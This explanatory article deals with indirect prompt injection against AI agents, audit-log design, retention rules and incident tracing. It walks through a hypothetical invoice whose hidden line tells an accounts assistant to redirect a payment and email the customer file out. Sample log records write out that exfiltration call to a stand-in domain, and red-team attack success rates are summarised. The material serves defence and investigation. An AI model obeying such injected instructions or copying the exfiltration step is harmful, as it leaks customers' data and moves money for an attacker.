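# Audit logs and limits on high-risk actions for AI systems that read untrusted content

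## Why assume that some injected instructions will be obeyed?

An AI agent is a system built on a language model that can take actions through software as well as write text. Companies use agents to answer email, search the web, write code and handle paperwork. Nearly all of this work involves reading untrusted content, which is anything that someone other than the agent's user or operator could have written. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in untrusted content to get the agent to follow them. The attacker only needs a way to put text where the agent will read it, and doesn't need access to the agent itself.

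No known method completely prevents AI agents from obeying instructions injected into the content they read. Developers train models to resist these instructions, and operators, assuming that some attacks will still succeed, add two controls. One is an audit trail, a lasting record of the requests an agent received, the material it read, the actions it took and the person or rule that allowed them. The other is a set of limits on high-risk actions, which are those that are hard to undo, reach outsiders, move money, expose private data or change permissions. Both controls cost money and slow the agent down, so whether they are worthwhile depends on how often agents obey injected instructions and whether better models will solve the problem.

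### How text turns into action

A plain chatbot takes in a text and returns another. Chu (2026), in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*, defines an agent as a system that also keeps state over many turns, carries out plans through sequences of actions, and changes its surroundings by calling tools. An agent does this by running a simple loop.

1. Software around the model assembles one input, which holds the operator's standing instructions, the user's request and a description of each available tool.
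2. The model produces text. Part of that text may be a tool call, a request to run a function, such as sending an email, with arguments that the model chose.
3. The software runs the function, using whatever passwords and permissions the operator gave the agent.
4. The software adds the result to the input and runs the model again on the longer text. The loop ends when the model writes an answer in place of a tool call.

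Untrusted content enters at step 4. When the agent opens an email, the email's text goes into the same input as the operator's instructions, and the model's next output depends on the whole input.

A hypothetical AI accounts assistant at a small wholesale company can read supplier emails, search the company's files, send email and pay bills. Each morning an employee asks it to deal with the new invoices. One invoice contains a line in white type on a white background, which a person wouldn't notice. According to this line, the supplier has changed banks, the payment should go to a new account, and the assistant should forward the customer file to an outside address so that the supplier can update its records. The software extracts the invoice's text, including the hidden line, and adds it to the model's input. If the model treats the line as part of its task, it finds the customer file, emails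 it to the outside address and pays the new account, using tools the company gave it for ordinary work.

Developers already test for attacks like this one. OpenAI, for example, has tested its models with sample attacks that included fraudulent payment instructions and the theft of an internal directory (The Hacker News, 2026).

### An input with no enforced boundary

SQL injection is an older, similar problem that has a cure. Programs query databases in a language called SQL, and a carelessly written website builds its queries by pasting a visitor's text into a command. A visitor who types a fragment of SQL into a form can then read or change the whole database. Parameterised queries prevent this. The program sends the command with empty slots and supplies the visitor's text separately, so the database engine treats that text as a value whatever it contains.

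David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an article that the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published in December 2025, argues that language models have no equivalent of the fix for SQL injection. A model works on tokens, the short pieces into which software splits text, and predicts the next token from all the tokens so far, whoever wrote them. It has no separate channel for commands. Developers can put tags around untrusted text such as an invoice, train the model to give the operator's words priority, or scan incoming text for suspicious phrases. Some of these measures make attacks harder, but none gives the model a built-in distinction between instructions and data. The tags are only more tokens, and a filter that blocks one phrasing of an attack misses many others.

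David C therefore compares the model to a confused deputy. In computer security, this is a program that uses its privileges on behalf of a less privileged party who has tricked it. For example, a printing service may be able to open every file on an office network. If an employee who has no right to read the payroll file asks the service to print it, and the service checks only its own permissions, it will print the file. Programmers can fix this flaw by making the service check the employee's permissions instead.

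That repair requires knowing reliably who is making a request. When the accounts assistant calls the payment tool, the call comes from the assistant in the employee's session, whether the instruction came from the employee or the invoice. This is why David C calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". Since some risk will remain, he advises designers to reduce its impact, chiefly with deterministic safeguards, meaning ordinary software outside the model that constrains the agent's actions without relying on the model's judgement. A simple example is to lower the agent's privileges to those of whoever wrote the content it is reading. Designers should plan for the worst that an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools. He thinks a language model may be a poor choice for a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

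Without a boundary between instructions and data, nobody can guarantee that a model will resist injection, but this doesn't establish how often a well-trained model will fail. A model that failed once in a billion attempts would need little protection around it. David C writes only that injection may never have a complete fix, and OpenAI conceded the same that month, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. The article also reports a more optimistic result. Anthropic's model Claude Opus 5 withstood every attack in 129 browser scenarios when it ran in Anthropic's own software. How much a system must rely on outside safeguards therefore depends on how often its model fails, which has to be measured.

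### How often attacks succeed

In 2025, reports that a defence stopped almost every attack were in doubt, because developers could base them on tests against a fixed list of known attacks. Nasr and colleagues showed that year, in *The Attacker Moves Second*, that stronger adaptive attacks, which an attacker adjusts to the specific defence, got past defences that had done well in such tests.

Since then, models have improved against fixed attacks, and the tests have become harsher. In late 2025, a test by the security company Gray Swan broke Opus 4.5 in 4.7% of cases with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, released in September, gives results from a newer Gray Swan test with 1,804 attacks that had worked well across several models.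 Fable 5.1 failed in 0.1% of cases with one attempt, 0.7% with ten and 1.0% with fifteen. With fifteen attempts, the best model from another developer failed in 9.2% of cases, and most failed in 24% to 53%. The fall from 4.7% to 0.1% is large, but it is only a rough guide to progress because the two tests used different attacks.

These were fixed attacks, though, and the results depend a good deal on which attacks are chosen. Opus 5 scored 2.0% at fifteen attempts when it came out. In the September results, after Gray Swan's set had grown by nine scenarios and 670 attacks, the same model scored 4.8%.

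Anthropic also reports tests against Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that searches for weaknesses and learns from its results. Gray Swan optimised Shade on the same scenarios it would later attack. A separate browser test reused attacks that had worked on an older model, Opus 4.7, without adapting them to the new models. Each cell in the table gives the share of attempts that succeeded, then the number of scenarios with at least one success. The safeguards are classifiers that inspect incoming text for injected instructions. The browser test also used a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls.

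| Test | Attempts per scenario | Fable 5.1, no safeguards | Fable 5.1, safeguards | Opus 5, no safeguards | Opus 5, safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding, stronger Shade attacker | 200 | 56.87%; 38 of 40 | 12.80%; 36 of 40 | 90.93%; 40 of 40 | 18.21%; 40 of 40 |
| Computer use (clicking and typing on a screen), Shade | 200 | 0.07%; 2 of 14 | 0.07%; 2 of 14 | 0.18%; 1 of 14 | 0.18%; 1 of 14 |
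| Browser, attacks not adapted | 10 | 2.64%; 10 of 110 | 0%; 0 of 110 | 2.09%; 7 of 110 | 0%; 0 of 110 |

Anthropic routes some of Fable 5.1's cyber security requests to an older model, Opus 4.8, and every successful attack on Fable 5.1 in the coding row came through that older model. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a breach. That is a good result for the newest model, but customers buy the two models together, and attacks on Opus 5 and the earlier Fable 5 succeeded directly against those models. Anthropic calls the test highly permissive, because real attackers seldom know the target system and risk detection with every try. That is fair, but an attacker who knows which commercial product a company uses can buy it and practise on it.

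An assistant that works through email and payment functions falls under what Gray Swan calls tool use. Fable 5.1 did best in this category, where no fixed attack succeeded within fifteen attempts. Anthropic's adaptive tests covered coding and computer use, so the best result for this type of assistant comes from fixed attacks, which are a weaker test than adaptive ones.

OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) reports that the company's latest models had saturated the common robustness tests, and that it had trained an AI attacker, GPT-Red, to find new weaknesses. GPT-Red succeeded in 84% of test scenarios, against 13% for human testers, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI is now using AI to attack its own AI*. In one trial it manipulated an AI-run vending machine in OpenAI's office, changing prices and cancelling other customers' orders. OpenAI used the results to train GPT-5.6 Sol, which fails a sixth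 as often as its predecessor on direct injections, the kind that someone types into the chat. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) points out that attacks succeed more often when they arrive through tools and outside content, as they would for an agent that reads invoices.

Developers' own figures are nearly impossible to compare. OpenAI publishes a robustness score against known attacks, where higher is better, while Anthropic publishes the share of attacks that succeed, partly against adaptive attackers. VentureBeat warns against reading the two on one scale. *FrontierBreach*, a November 2026 benchmark from the security vendor PromptArmor, compares models from different developers by inserting attacks modelled on real incidents into office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio. Even against the best-scoring model, Gemini 4 Carbon,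 attacks succeeded in 2.4% of cases. The rate was 7.6% for GPT-6 Astra, 10.0% for Claude Fable 5.2 and 91.4% for Grok 4.5. PromptArmor labels these results k = 5, which by the usual convention means five attempts per case, and a pipeline generated the cases beforehand. The margins of error, two to four points for the leading models, are too wide to rank models with similar scores, and PromptArmor has a commercial interest in reporting high attack success rates.

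A company that processes thousands of invoices may well choose a small model because it is cheap. One such model, Anthropic's Haiku 5.5, released in October 2026, largely matches Anthropic's bigger models against adaptive attackers. But Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* that it is less resistant to injected instructions than Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 on Gray Swan's benchmark, mostly when it operates a screen.

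Much of the research on defences uses AgentDojo, a public test suite that gives agents ordinary tasks and puts injected instructions in what they read. It measures both whether the agent finished the user's task and whether it carried out the attacker's, so a defence cannot score well just by making the agent useless.

### What a low rate means over many attempts

If each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is 1 − (1 − p)^n. Fable 5.1's average failure rate against a single fixed attack is 0.1%. Suppose a criminal who doesn't mind which company pays sends the doctored invoice to 1,000 companies whose assistants all fail at that rate. The chance that at least one company pays is 1 − 0.999^1000, or about 63%.

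Real attempts are not independent, so the formula can be far off. For Opus 4.5, with p at 4.7%, it predicts a success rate of 38% after ten attempts and 99% after a hundred, but Gray Swan measured 33.6% and 63%. For Opus 4.6 working on a screen in February 2026, 17.8% of single attempts succeeded. At that rate, the formula predicts that a breach within 200 attempts is almost certain, but VentureBeat reports a measured rate of 78.6%, or 57.1% with safeguards.

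The gap arises because some situations are more vulnerable than others, which an average doesn't show. If half of all scenarios were immune and the other half failed 9.4% of the time, the average for one attempt would still be 4.7%, but no number of attempts could push the overall success rate above 50%. Anthropic's computer-use test of Opus 5 showed this on a small scale. All five successes, out of 2,800 attempts, were in one of the 14 scenarios, whereas independent attempts at the same average rate would have breached about four scenarios. This shouldn't reassure an operator much, because nobody knows in advance whether a particular assistant, with its tools and instructions, is one of the weak cases.

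Copies of one attack also tend to succeed or fail together. If 1,000 companies run the same assistant on the same model, an invoice that fools one company's assistant will probably fool many others. The expected number of victims is still one, but usually no company pays, and occasionally many pay at about the same time.

Attackers also learn, so a persistent one may do better than the formula predicts from early failures. Gray Swan ran a public contest in which 464 people made more than 272,000 attempts on 13 models, and 8,648 of those attempts succeeded. An attack counted only if it made the agent do something harmful and conceal it from the user. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5%, and successes kept coming at a roughly constant pace for the whole three weeks. David C expects most attackers to need several tries to hone an attack, and recommends logging enough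 of an agent's inputs, outputs and tool calls to spot the failed tries early.

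## What should the audit trail record, and for how long?

David C wants logs that reveal failed attacks early. An audit trail also has to help people investigate attacks discovered much later. If the accounts assistant emails the customer file to a criminal in December, the company may first hear of it in March, when customers complain about fraudulent bills. An investigator can then work out what the assistant read, what it did and which rule allowed it only if the software recorded the relevant facts at the time.

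### The fields of a record

| Field | Question | Example from the accounts assistant |
|---|---|---|
| User and agent identity | Who or what acted, and for whom? | Accounts assistant 3.2, in J. Patel's session |
| Model and version | Which model chose the action? | The exact release that answered |
| User's request | What had the person asked for? | "Deal with the new invoices" |
| Items read, with origin and a copy or hash | What text entered the model's input, and who could have written it? | Text of an invoice from an outside sender |
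| Tool calls, with exact arguments and results | What did the agent try to do, and what happened? | An email, its recipient and its attachment |
| Permission in force | What could the agent have done at that moment? | Send email to any address |
| Policy decision | Which rule allowed or refused the call? | Payment refused because of an unknown bank account |
| Human approval | Who agreed, and to what? | The name of the approver and the text on the screen |
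| Timestamps | In what order did things happen? | Invoice read 12 seconds before the email |
| Linking identifiers | Which entries in other systems belong to this run? | The mail server's number for the sent message |

The identity field has to separate the agent from the person it works for. *13 million tool calls*, an article by Elastic, which sells search and security software, explains that a coding agent runs commands under the developer's own account. Security software on the laptop therefore can't distinguish the agent's commands from those the developer typed.

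The model field should name the model that answered, which may differ from the one the company requested. Anthropic reroutes some of Fable 5.1's requests to an older model, so a log that recorded only "Fable 5.1" could lead an investigator to examine the wrong model.

For items read, the most useful copy is the text that went into the model's input. A person who opens the doctored invoice won't notice the hidden line, but it is visible in the extracted text. The original file is worth keeping too, since it shows how the attacker hid the instruction. A web address alone is weak evidence, because the page's owner can change the page after the agent visits. Anyone can forge an email sender's address, so the origin field for an email should also include the result of the mail system's check on the sender.

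A hash is a short string that software computes from a piece of data. Changing one character of the data produces a different hash, so anyone who still has a copy can check whether it matches what the agent read. But nobody can read the invoice from its hash, so the company can't recover the attacker's instruction if it kept only the hash and the email is gone.

The permission in force and the policy decision can differ. The assistant may have permission to pay bills up to £5,000, while a policy check (a test that software outside the model applies to each tool call) refuses a particular bill. Administrators also change permissions, so an investigator who looks them up in March may find different ones from those in force in December. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises organisations to log administrators' changes, such as newly enabled plugins.

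### Four records from one morning

In this hypothetical run, the first record lists the user, the agent, the model and the request, which stay the same throughout. Later records refer to it by the run's identifier. The software then writes the following four records.

```
1  time        2026-12-01 09:14:07.210 UTC
   run, call   R-0412, C-03
   action      read_attachment
   arguments   email E-88213, file invoice-2291.pdf
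   origin      outside sender, billing@northfield.example
   permission  accounts mailbox, read only
   policy      allowed, rule MAIL-1
   result      text T-551, hash e07b41...; file hash 9c4120...
```

2  time        2026-12-01 09:14:12.845 UTC
   run, call   R-0412, C-04
   action      search_files
   arguments   "customer file"
   origin      company file store, customers.xlsx, version 88
   permission  company files, read only
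   policy      allowed, rule FILE-1
   result      text T-552, hash 41d9f3...

3  time        2026-12-01 09:14:19.330 UTC
   run, call   R-0412, C-05
   action      send_email
   arguments   to records@northfield-update.example,
               body T-553, attachment customers.xlsx
   permission  send email, any recipient
   policy      allowed, rule MAIL-4; no approval required
   result      sent, mail server message M-90417

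4  time        2026-12-01 09:14:24.102 UTC
   run, call   R-0412, C-06
   action      pay_bill
   arguments   invoice 2291, GBP 1,840.00,
               account 00-00-00 55667731
   permission  pay invoices up to GBP 5,000
   policy      refused, rule PAY-2, account not in supplier register
   result      not run
```

The policy check stopped the payment, but the attack still got the customer file out of the company because the assistant's permission covered any recipient. An investigator can see both facts here, open text T-551 to read the hidden line, and use the identifiers to start tracing the email back to the invoice.

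An ordinary application log would contain much less. Programmers write these logs mainly to find faults, so a typical one would show that Patel's session called the payment service at 09:14:24 and received an error. The email would appear as a routine success, if it appeared at all. AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails* warns against logging only errors, because nobody can then reconstruct the full sequence of events. This matters especially for injection, because the harmful actions are the ones that succeed and so produce no error to log.

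Even a good conventional security log may not record what an AI agent read before it acted. The US standards agency NIST, in its catalogue of controls SP 800-53, asks for records that establish what happened, when and where, the source and outcome of the event, and who or what was involved. A log could meet that description for the email in record 3 without mentioning the invoice. Investigators seldom need to know what else conventional software had been reading, because it follows its code and its user's commands, but an agent's next action depends on everything in its input.

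### Microsoft's Copilot log

Microsoft automatically logs use of Copilot, its family of AI assistants, for organisations that have auditing switched on. Each record includes the user, the time, the application, the agent and its version, and the model's name, version and developer.

The most important part for injection is AccessedResources, which lists every file, email or other item that Copilot used for the request. Each entry gives the item's identifier, location, sensitivity label and type of access, such as reading or modifying. If a policy blocked or restricted the access, the PolicyDetails field can name the policy and its rules. Another field, XPIADetected, shows whether Microsoft's software detected an injection attack in that item, so a positive result identifies the suspect document. XPIA stands for cross prompt injection attack, Microsoft's name for indirect prompt injection.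 A negative result is less informative because the detector may have missed an attack, and the attacks that detectors miss are the most likely to do harm.

A separate list covers the messages in the conversation. Each entry has an identifier, a marker showing whether the message is the user's prompt or Copilot's response, and a flag for a detected jailbreak, which is an attempt by the user to get the model to break its rules. The entry doesn't contain the message's text, so an investigator has to find it in the system that stores the conversation. Microsoft's list of common properties also has no field for the exact arguments of a tool call or for a hash of the content that Copilot read. If someone edits a document after Copilot has read it, the document's identifier will lead to the edited version unless the file store keeps old versions.

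When Copilot searches the web, the record lists BingWebSearch as a plugin, which shows that a search took place but not which pages it returned.

Microsoft will also log the use of other companies' AI applications. It charges for these records by volume and keeps them for 180 days. A customer who relies on another supplier's own log has to find out what it contains. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre suggests that, before buying, customers ask what logging is available for prompts, sources and tool actions.

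### Two attempts at a common format

OpenTelemetry is an open-source project that defines shared names for monitoring data, so that one company's tools can read another's records. Its basic unit is the span, a timed record of one operation, such as a call to a model or a run of a tool. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines the fields for AI systems and ranks them from required to opt-in. Software must record the type of operation and the model's provider. It should record the tool's name and the tool call's identifier, and a conversation identifier when it has one. Separate fields record the name of the model requested and the name of the one that produced the response, which would expose the rerouting problem.

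The conventions make recording all content opt-in, including the user's messages, the model's output, the operator's standing instructions, and the arguments and results of tool calls. By default, the accounts assistant's theft would appear as one run of a tool called send_email, with an identifier and a time but no recipient or attachment. A company that adopts the conventions for security has to turn on the fields it will need.

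The format may also change. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, reports that the project moved these conventions to their own repository in June 2026. On 21 August they were still marked as under development, with no official release.

*Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a format designed for auditing from the start. It is one individual's Internet-Draft at the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes many of the internet's technical standards. The IETF hasn't adopted it as a standard, and the draft expires on 19 February 2027 unless a new version replaces it.

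Sharif makes twelve fields mandatory, including the agent's identity and version, the session, the type of action and its outcome. An outcome can be success, failure, timeout, denied or escalated, and nine suggested codes give the reason for a denial, such as a missing permission. The record_phase field shows whether the software wrote the record before, during or after the action. A record written after a payment can't prove that a check came first, so Sharif requires software to record refusals and referrals to a person before the action would have run. In systems that the EU's AI Act classes as high-risk, each payment gets one record for the decision beforehand and another for the result.

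Sharif's draft goes further than OpenTelemetry's defaults and forbids raw inputs and outputs in audit records. In its worked example, an agent transfers £500 in a session of six records, which cover the start, a sanctions check, its response, the decision to approve, the payment and the close. The records give the amount, the currency and the policy, but they include the payment's arguments only as a hash, so nobody could learn from them who received the money. The draft allows companies to keep raw data in a separate system, linked by record number, and an investigation into prompt injection would need that system. The draft also defines no field for who wrote the content in a tool's response, so the format wouldn't distinguish a stranger's invoice from an internal file.

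### Elastic's deployment

Elastic gave hundreds of developers an AI coding agent, Cursor, and then realised that it had no record of what the agent did. Cursor can run an outside program at set points, for example before it reads a file or runs a command. Elastic wrote a 280-line script that adds a line to a log at each of these points, and software already on the developers' laptops sends the log to a central database.

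In the two months after the rollout in May 2026, Elastic collected more than 13 million events from over 1,100 machines and nearly 900 users, or about 200 events per machine per day. File reads outnumbered commands by roughly four to one, which surprised the staff. A log of only the agent's commands and edits would have missed most of what it did, including the file reads, through which untrusted text can enter.

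The log also gave Elastic a more accurate inventory of its own systems. Agents often reach outside tools through servers that use a standard called the Model Context Protocol, and each server is a third party that an attacker could compromise. Before the project, Elastic listed only the servers that people remembered to mention. Using the log, Elastic found more than 300, and 86% of them had only one or two users.

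The first version of the script stored who was acting and the raw data that Cursor supplied for each event. The data was complete, but the same fact was stored in a different place for each type of event, which made the records very hard to search. Elastic then moved the command, file path, tool name and server into fixed fields at the top of every record. Investigators could then use a single query to list the machines on which an agent had read a credentials file, or the commands that downloaded a program and immediately ran it.

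Elastic decided not to collect file contents, prompts or model responses, and told employees so before the rollout. It reports that nobody objected to the premise. The company acknowledges that, as a result, it could detect an injected agent only through its actions. In the accounts assistant's case, such a log would record that the agent opened an invoice and then sent an email, but not the hidden line in the invoice that led it to send the email.

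The boundary is also less firm than it sounds, because the script still stores Cursor's original data alongside the fixed fields. Elastic values this because it captures any new field that Cursor adds, but a future version of Cursor could put content into the log without anyone at Elastic deciding to collect it. Command lines can also contain passwords. The article reports no attack that the log caught or explained, so it is evidence that logging at this scale is affordable and acceptable to staff, but provides little evidence of how well such a log works against injection.

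| | Microsoft | OpenTelemetry | Sharif | Elastic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model | Name, version, developer | Model requested and model that answered | Optional | Name |
| Conversation text | Identifiers | Opt-in | Hashes | Not collected |
| Items read | Identifier, location, sensitivity label | Opt-in | Hash of the tool's response | File path |
| Tool arguments | No listed field | Opt-in | Hash | Full command lines |
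| Refusals | Policy that blocked access to an item | No dedicated field | Outcome and reason | None, as the script allows every action |
| Human approval | No listed field | No dedicated field | Optional | No listed field |

### Full content or metadata?

All four formats keep the text of conversations out of the log by default. David C, however, suggests that logs might include the model's full input and output. He has a good reason, because an injection is text. Metadata, the facts about a message or file other than its contents, can show that the assistant read invoice 2291 and then emailed the customer file, but the content is needed to show that the invoice contained an instruction to do so.

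There are also strong reasons not to log full content. An agent's input can include customers' details, staff matters, contracts and passwords. Copying all of it into a log gathers material from many separate systems in one place, where people who had no access to the originals can often read it. A thief who breaks into the log gets everything the agent has read, which may be more than an injection attack could have extracted. The log will also contain any injected instructions, so a company that has another AI agent read its logs exposes that agent to untrusted content.

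An audit log can record everything the model received in much less space if it saves each new item once, along with the order in which the items appeared. The software sends the model the whole conversation again at every step, so if each of k steps adds s words, logging every input in full stores s × k(k + 1)/2 words. For a run of 20 steps that each add 2,000 words, that is 420,000 words, compared with 40,000 if each item is saved once. This works only if the software also logs any shortening or summarising of earlier text, since the model then receives something different from the original items.

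Companies can reduce the privacy cost in several ways, each with its own weakness.

**Redaction** removes sensitive details from the log. AWS recommends doing it before the log is stored, because afterwards every person and program with access to the log becomes a data protection concern. Passwords and access keys are easy to redact, because an investigator needs to know which key the agent used but never needs the key itself. Bank details are harder, because a filter that blanks out account numbers to protect suppliers would also delete the criminal's account number from record 4. One answer is to replace each number with a code that stays the same wherever the number occurs, and to keep the list matching codes to numbers under tighter control.

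Hashes let a company check a copy without storing the content, but they don't hide short or predictable data well. An eight-digit account number has only 100 million possible values, so an ordinary computer can hash all of them within minutes and see which one matches. Mixing a secret key into the calculation prevents this if the key is stored separately from the log.

**Separate access** means keeping metadata in the main log and content in another store with its own permissions. OpenTelemetry recommends this for live systems that handle sensitive data or large volumes. Elastic has no content store, but it similarly restricts access to its metadata by hiding the agent fields from general security staff, so only a small team can see them.

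For agents that read untrusted content, a company can also decide what to copy in full based on where the material came from. Internal files such as the customer list are already stored in a company system, and if that system keeps old versions, the audit trail needs only an identifier, a version number and a hash. The company can keep full copies of outside emails and web pages, which may change or vanish and are usually where the injected instruction will be. This preserves most of the evidence while duplicating far fewer of the company's secrets. Customers' emails still contain personal data, so the store of copies needs access limits and a deletion date like any other.

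### How long to keep it

AWS recommends keeping logs for 7 to 14 days if they help developers fix faults, 30 to 90 days if they support incident investigations, and one to seven years if they prove compliance with regulations. Varying the period saves money because the bulkiest logs are deleted first.

How long the company keeps copies of what the agent read should depend on how long the harm would take to come to light. These copies are large and developers use them to fix faults, so they could easily end up in the shortest retention category, which would be a mistake. If the customer file leaks on 1 December and customers first complain in March, even a 90-day log may have lost the earliest records. The company would still have a compliance record of the email, but not the invoice text it refers to. Once someone suspects an attack, the company should also suspend automatic deletion for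 the runs concerned.

Metadata takes up so little space that it can be kept much longer. Sharif estimates that an agent producing 10,000 records a day needs 3.6 to 7.2 gigabytes a year, before compression. He recommends keeping records for twelve months for high-risk systems and six months for others.

People may have a legal right to have their data erased before then. Each record in Sharif's format contains a hash of the previous one, which helps to reveal tampering, so deleting a record would break the sequence. Software instead replaces it with a tombstone, an entry that keeps the record's number, time and hash and gives the reason for the deletion. Erasure is easier for a company that stores content separately, because it can often delete the copy of an email and leave the metadata in place.

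### Legal duties in the European Union

The EU's AI Act imposes logging duties on high-risk systems, a legal category that is separate from high-risk actions. FEDIL, a Luxembourg business federation, lists employment screening, credit scoring, education and critical infrastructure among the uses the category covers. It also includes AI in some regulated products, such as medical devices. An assistant that pays suppliers' invoices probably falls outside the category, but a system that screens job applicants falls within it and routinely reads untrusted content. David C gives the example of a CV whose hidden text tells such a system's model to approve the candidate for interview.

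Three articles deal with logs.

- Article 12 requires high-risk systems to be technically capable of recording events automatically throughout their lifetime. According to the European Commission's *Article 12*, the logs must cover events that help to identify risks and substantial modifications, to monitor the system after its sale and to monitor its operation. The article sets minimum fields only for remote biometric identification, such as recognising faces at a distance. These are the start and end of each use, the reference database, the input that produced a match and the people who verified the result.
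- Article 19 applies to providers, the companies that develop a system and put it on the market. As artificialintelligenceact.eu reproduces the text, they must keep the automatic logs under their control for a period that suits the system's purpose, and for at least six months.
- Article 26 places the same minimum on deployers, the organisations that use the system, according to the European Commission's *Article 26*. Employers must also inform workers and their representatives before using a high-risk system at the workplace.

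Both retention rules apply unless other EU or national law, particularly data protection law, sets a different period. Financial institutions keep the logs as part of the records that financial law already requires.

None of these duties applies yet. They were due to start on 2 August 2026, but the EU amended the Act through the Digital Omnibus on AI, which took effect on 27 July, according to the law firm Cooley. The final text from the Council of the European Union (2026) moves the start to 2 December 2027 for uses such as employment screening, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products. For those products, the Commission may also limit the duties in Articles 12 and 19 where other product laws protect people at least as well. Machinery moves to its own sector's rules, which the Commission must update to reflect the Act's requirements. Sharif's draft, published three weeks after the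 amendment, still gives August 2026 as the starting date and wrongly applies the minimum fields for biometric systems to every high-risk system.

The common 180-day retention setting is shorter than the six-month minimum, because six calendar months always contain at least 181 days. Microsoft keeps its logs of other companies' AI applications for 180 days, so an organisation that relied on those logs for a high-risk system would have to export them before they expired.

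Technical standards are meant to fill in the detail that Article 12 leaves out, but most don't exist yet. The European Parliament's *AI Act* (2025), a briefing its research service updated in October 2026, reports that the European standards bodies missed deadlines in April and August 2025. They have since published one harmonised standard, on quality management for companies that provide AI systems. A system that follows a harmonised standard is presumed to comply with the corresponding part of the law. David C ties his advice to TS 104 223, a specification of baseline security requirements for AI from the European standards body ETSI, but following that specification creates no such presumption.

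## How do logs lead from a harmful action back to the injected instruction?

Investigators usually learn of an attack from its results and have to work backwards. In the accounts assistant's case, they trace customers' complaints in March back to one hidden line in an invoice from 1 December. Complete records make this example fairly easy. Tracing is harder when a run contains hundreds of calls, when the attacker's words don't reappear in the harmful action, or when the company needs proof that the text caused the action rather than merely preceded it.

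### An investigation from start to finish

An investigation may begin with a complaint, an alert or a series of failed tool calls. David C suggests that an operator who looks into failed calls may discover an attack while the attacker is still refining it. The accounts assistant's refused payment was such a warning, logged three months before any customer complained. But calls also fail in ordinary work, for instance when a genuine supplier changes banks, so one refusal proves little. Refusals are much more suspicious when several name the same unknown account or follow emails from the same sender. David C gives no figures for how many attacks this catches, and an attacker who practises on a private copy of the same product leaves no failed calls in the victim's log.

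The investigator then identifies the run by matching the message number in two logs. The mail server's log shows that message M-90417 carried the customer file to an outside address, and the same number appears in the agent's record of call C-05 in run R-0412. Some products require several tools for this step. *Investigating M365 Copilot Activity with Sentinel & Defender XDR* (Lepakshi, 2025) explains that security staff can search Copilot activity across all users in one table, but have to look up the prompts and responses in a second tool.

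The next step is to list everything that was in the model's input when it chose to send the email. In this run, that includes the operator's standing instructions, Patel's request, any notes the assistant had saved from earlier sessions, the invoice text T-551 and the search result T-552. Checking only the last item before the email, the company's own customer file, would not be enough, because an injected instruction stays in the input and can take effect many steps later.

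To find the source, the investigator searches the listed items for the recipient's address, records@northfield-update.example, and finds it only in the invoice's hidden line. That makes call C-03 the injection point, the step at which the malicious text entered the model's input.

From there the investigator reads forwards and treats every later action as suspect, including those that look routine. In this case, those actions are a file search, an email and a refused payment. The investigator also has to check anything the assistant saved. If the assistant had written itself a note that Northfield had changed banks, that note could enter its input every morning, even after the invoice was gone.

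If an attack is still under way, containment can't wait for the full list. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises organisations to judge the severity first, by asking whether data leaked, whether the assistant changed any records and whether it has broad permissions. They should then stop the harm before working out its full extent. For a prompt injection, the centre recommends blocking the document or email so that the agent can't retrieve it again, and temporarily requiring human approval. If the agent has misused its tools, the centre recommends switching them off or making them read-only, and revoking or replacing the credentials behind them. It also recommends making containment reversible, which is sensible because the first guess about the cause may be wrong.

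The company should also clear poisoned notes from the assistant's saved memory, after copying them as evidence. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI)'s *AI Incident Response Framework* (2026) has separate playbooks for prompt injection and memory injection. CoSAI's *Defending AI Systems* stresses recording changes to memory before any incident. Without a record of which run wrote each note, the company would have to delete everything the assistant had saved or guess which notes were safe.

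Finally, the investigator searches other runs for the same attack. Searching by the invoice's hash quickly finds exact copies but misses reworded ones. However, every version has to name a bank account or an address that the criminal controls, and new accounts take effort to open. Searching for the account number and the internet domain may therefore find attacks that share no other words with the original.

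### Three ways to trace an action

Searching for an address works only when the attack puts one in the tool call. *AgentTracer* (Yao, Wu and colleagues, 2026) sorts the methods for harder cases into three families: dependency graphs, attribution scores, and tests that remove or replace part of the input.

A dependency graph has a point for each action or item of data, and an arrow wherever one fed into another. The investigator starts at the harmful action and follows the arrows back. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a graph called Agent-BOM, which connects an agent's lasting parts, such as its tools and long-term memory, to the goals, reasoning and actions of a particular run. An audit finds a suspicious entry, traces it back to its source and forward to its effects, then checks details such as permissions along the path. Li and colleagues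 used the graph to reconstruct four composite attacks, one of which passed from one session to another through the agent's memory.

Software can easily link two calls when the output of one reappears in the arguments of the next, but language models often don't repeat text word for word. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) gives the example of a research agent that reads a web page with a hidden instruction to include a confidential patient note in its memo, rewritten in polished language. The memo then shares no exact wording with the note. A rule that flagged every path from a web page to a report would catch this attack, but it would also flag every legitimate research memo.

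An injection can also change which tool the agent calls without supplying any of the text in the call. For example, an email might tell the agent to run a certain program if a condition is met. Cai and colleagues give the example of a search result that tells an agent to send its findings to an outside server. A text search would find the server's address in both the search result and the call, although they write that such attacks leave no data footprint. Delay is a third difficulty, because an agent may store a document's contents on day 1 and use them in a report on day 4, when the new session's log no longer shows where they came from.

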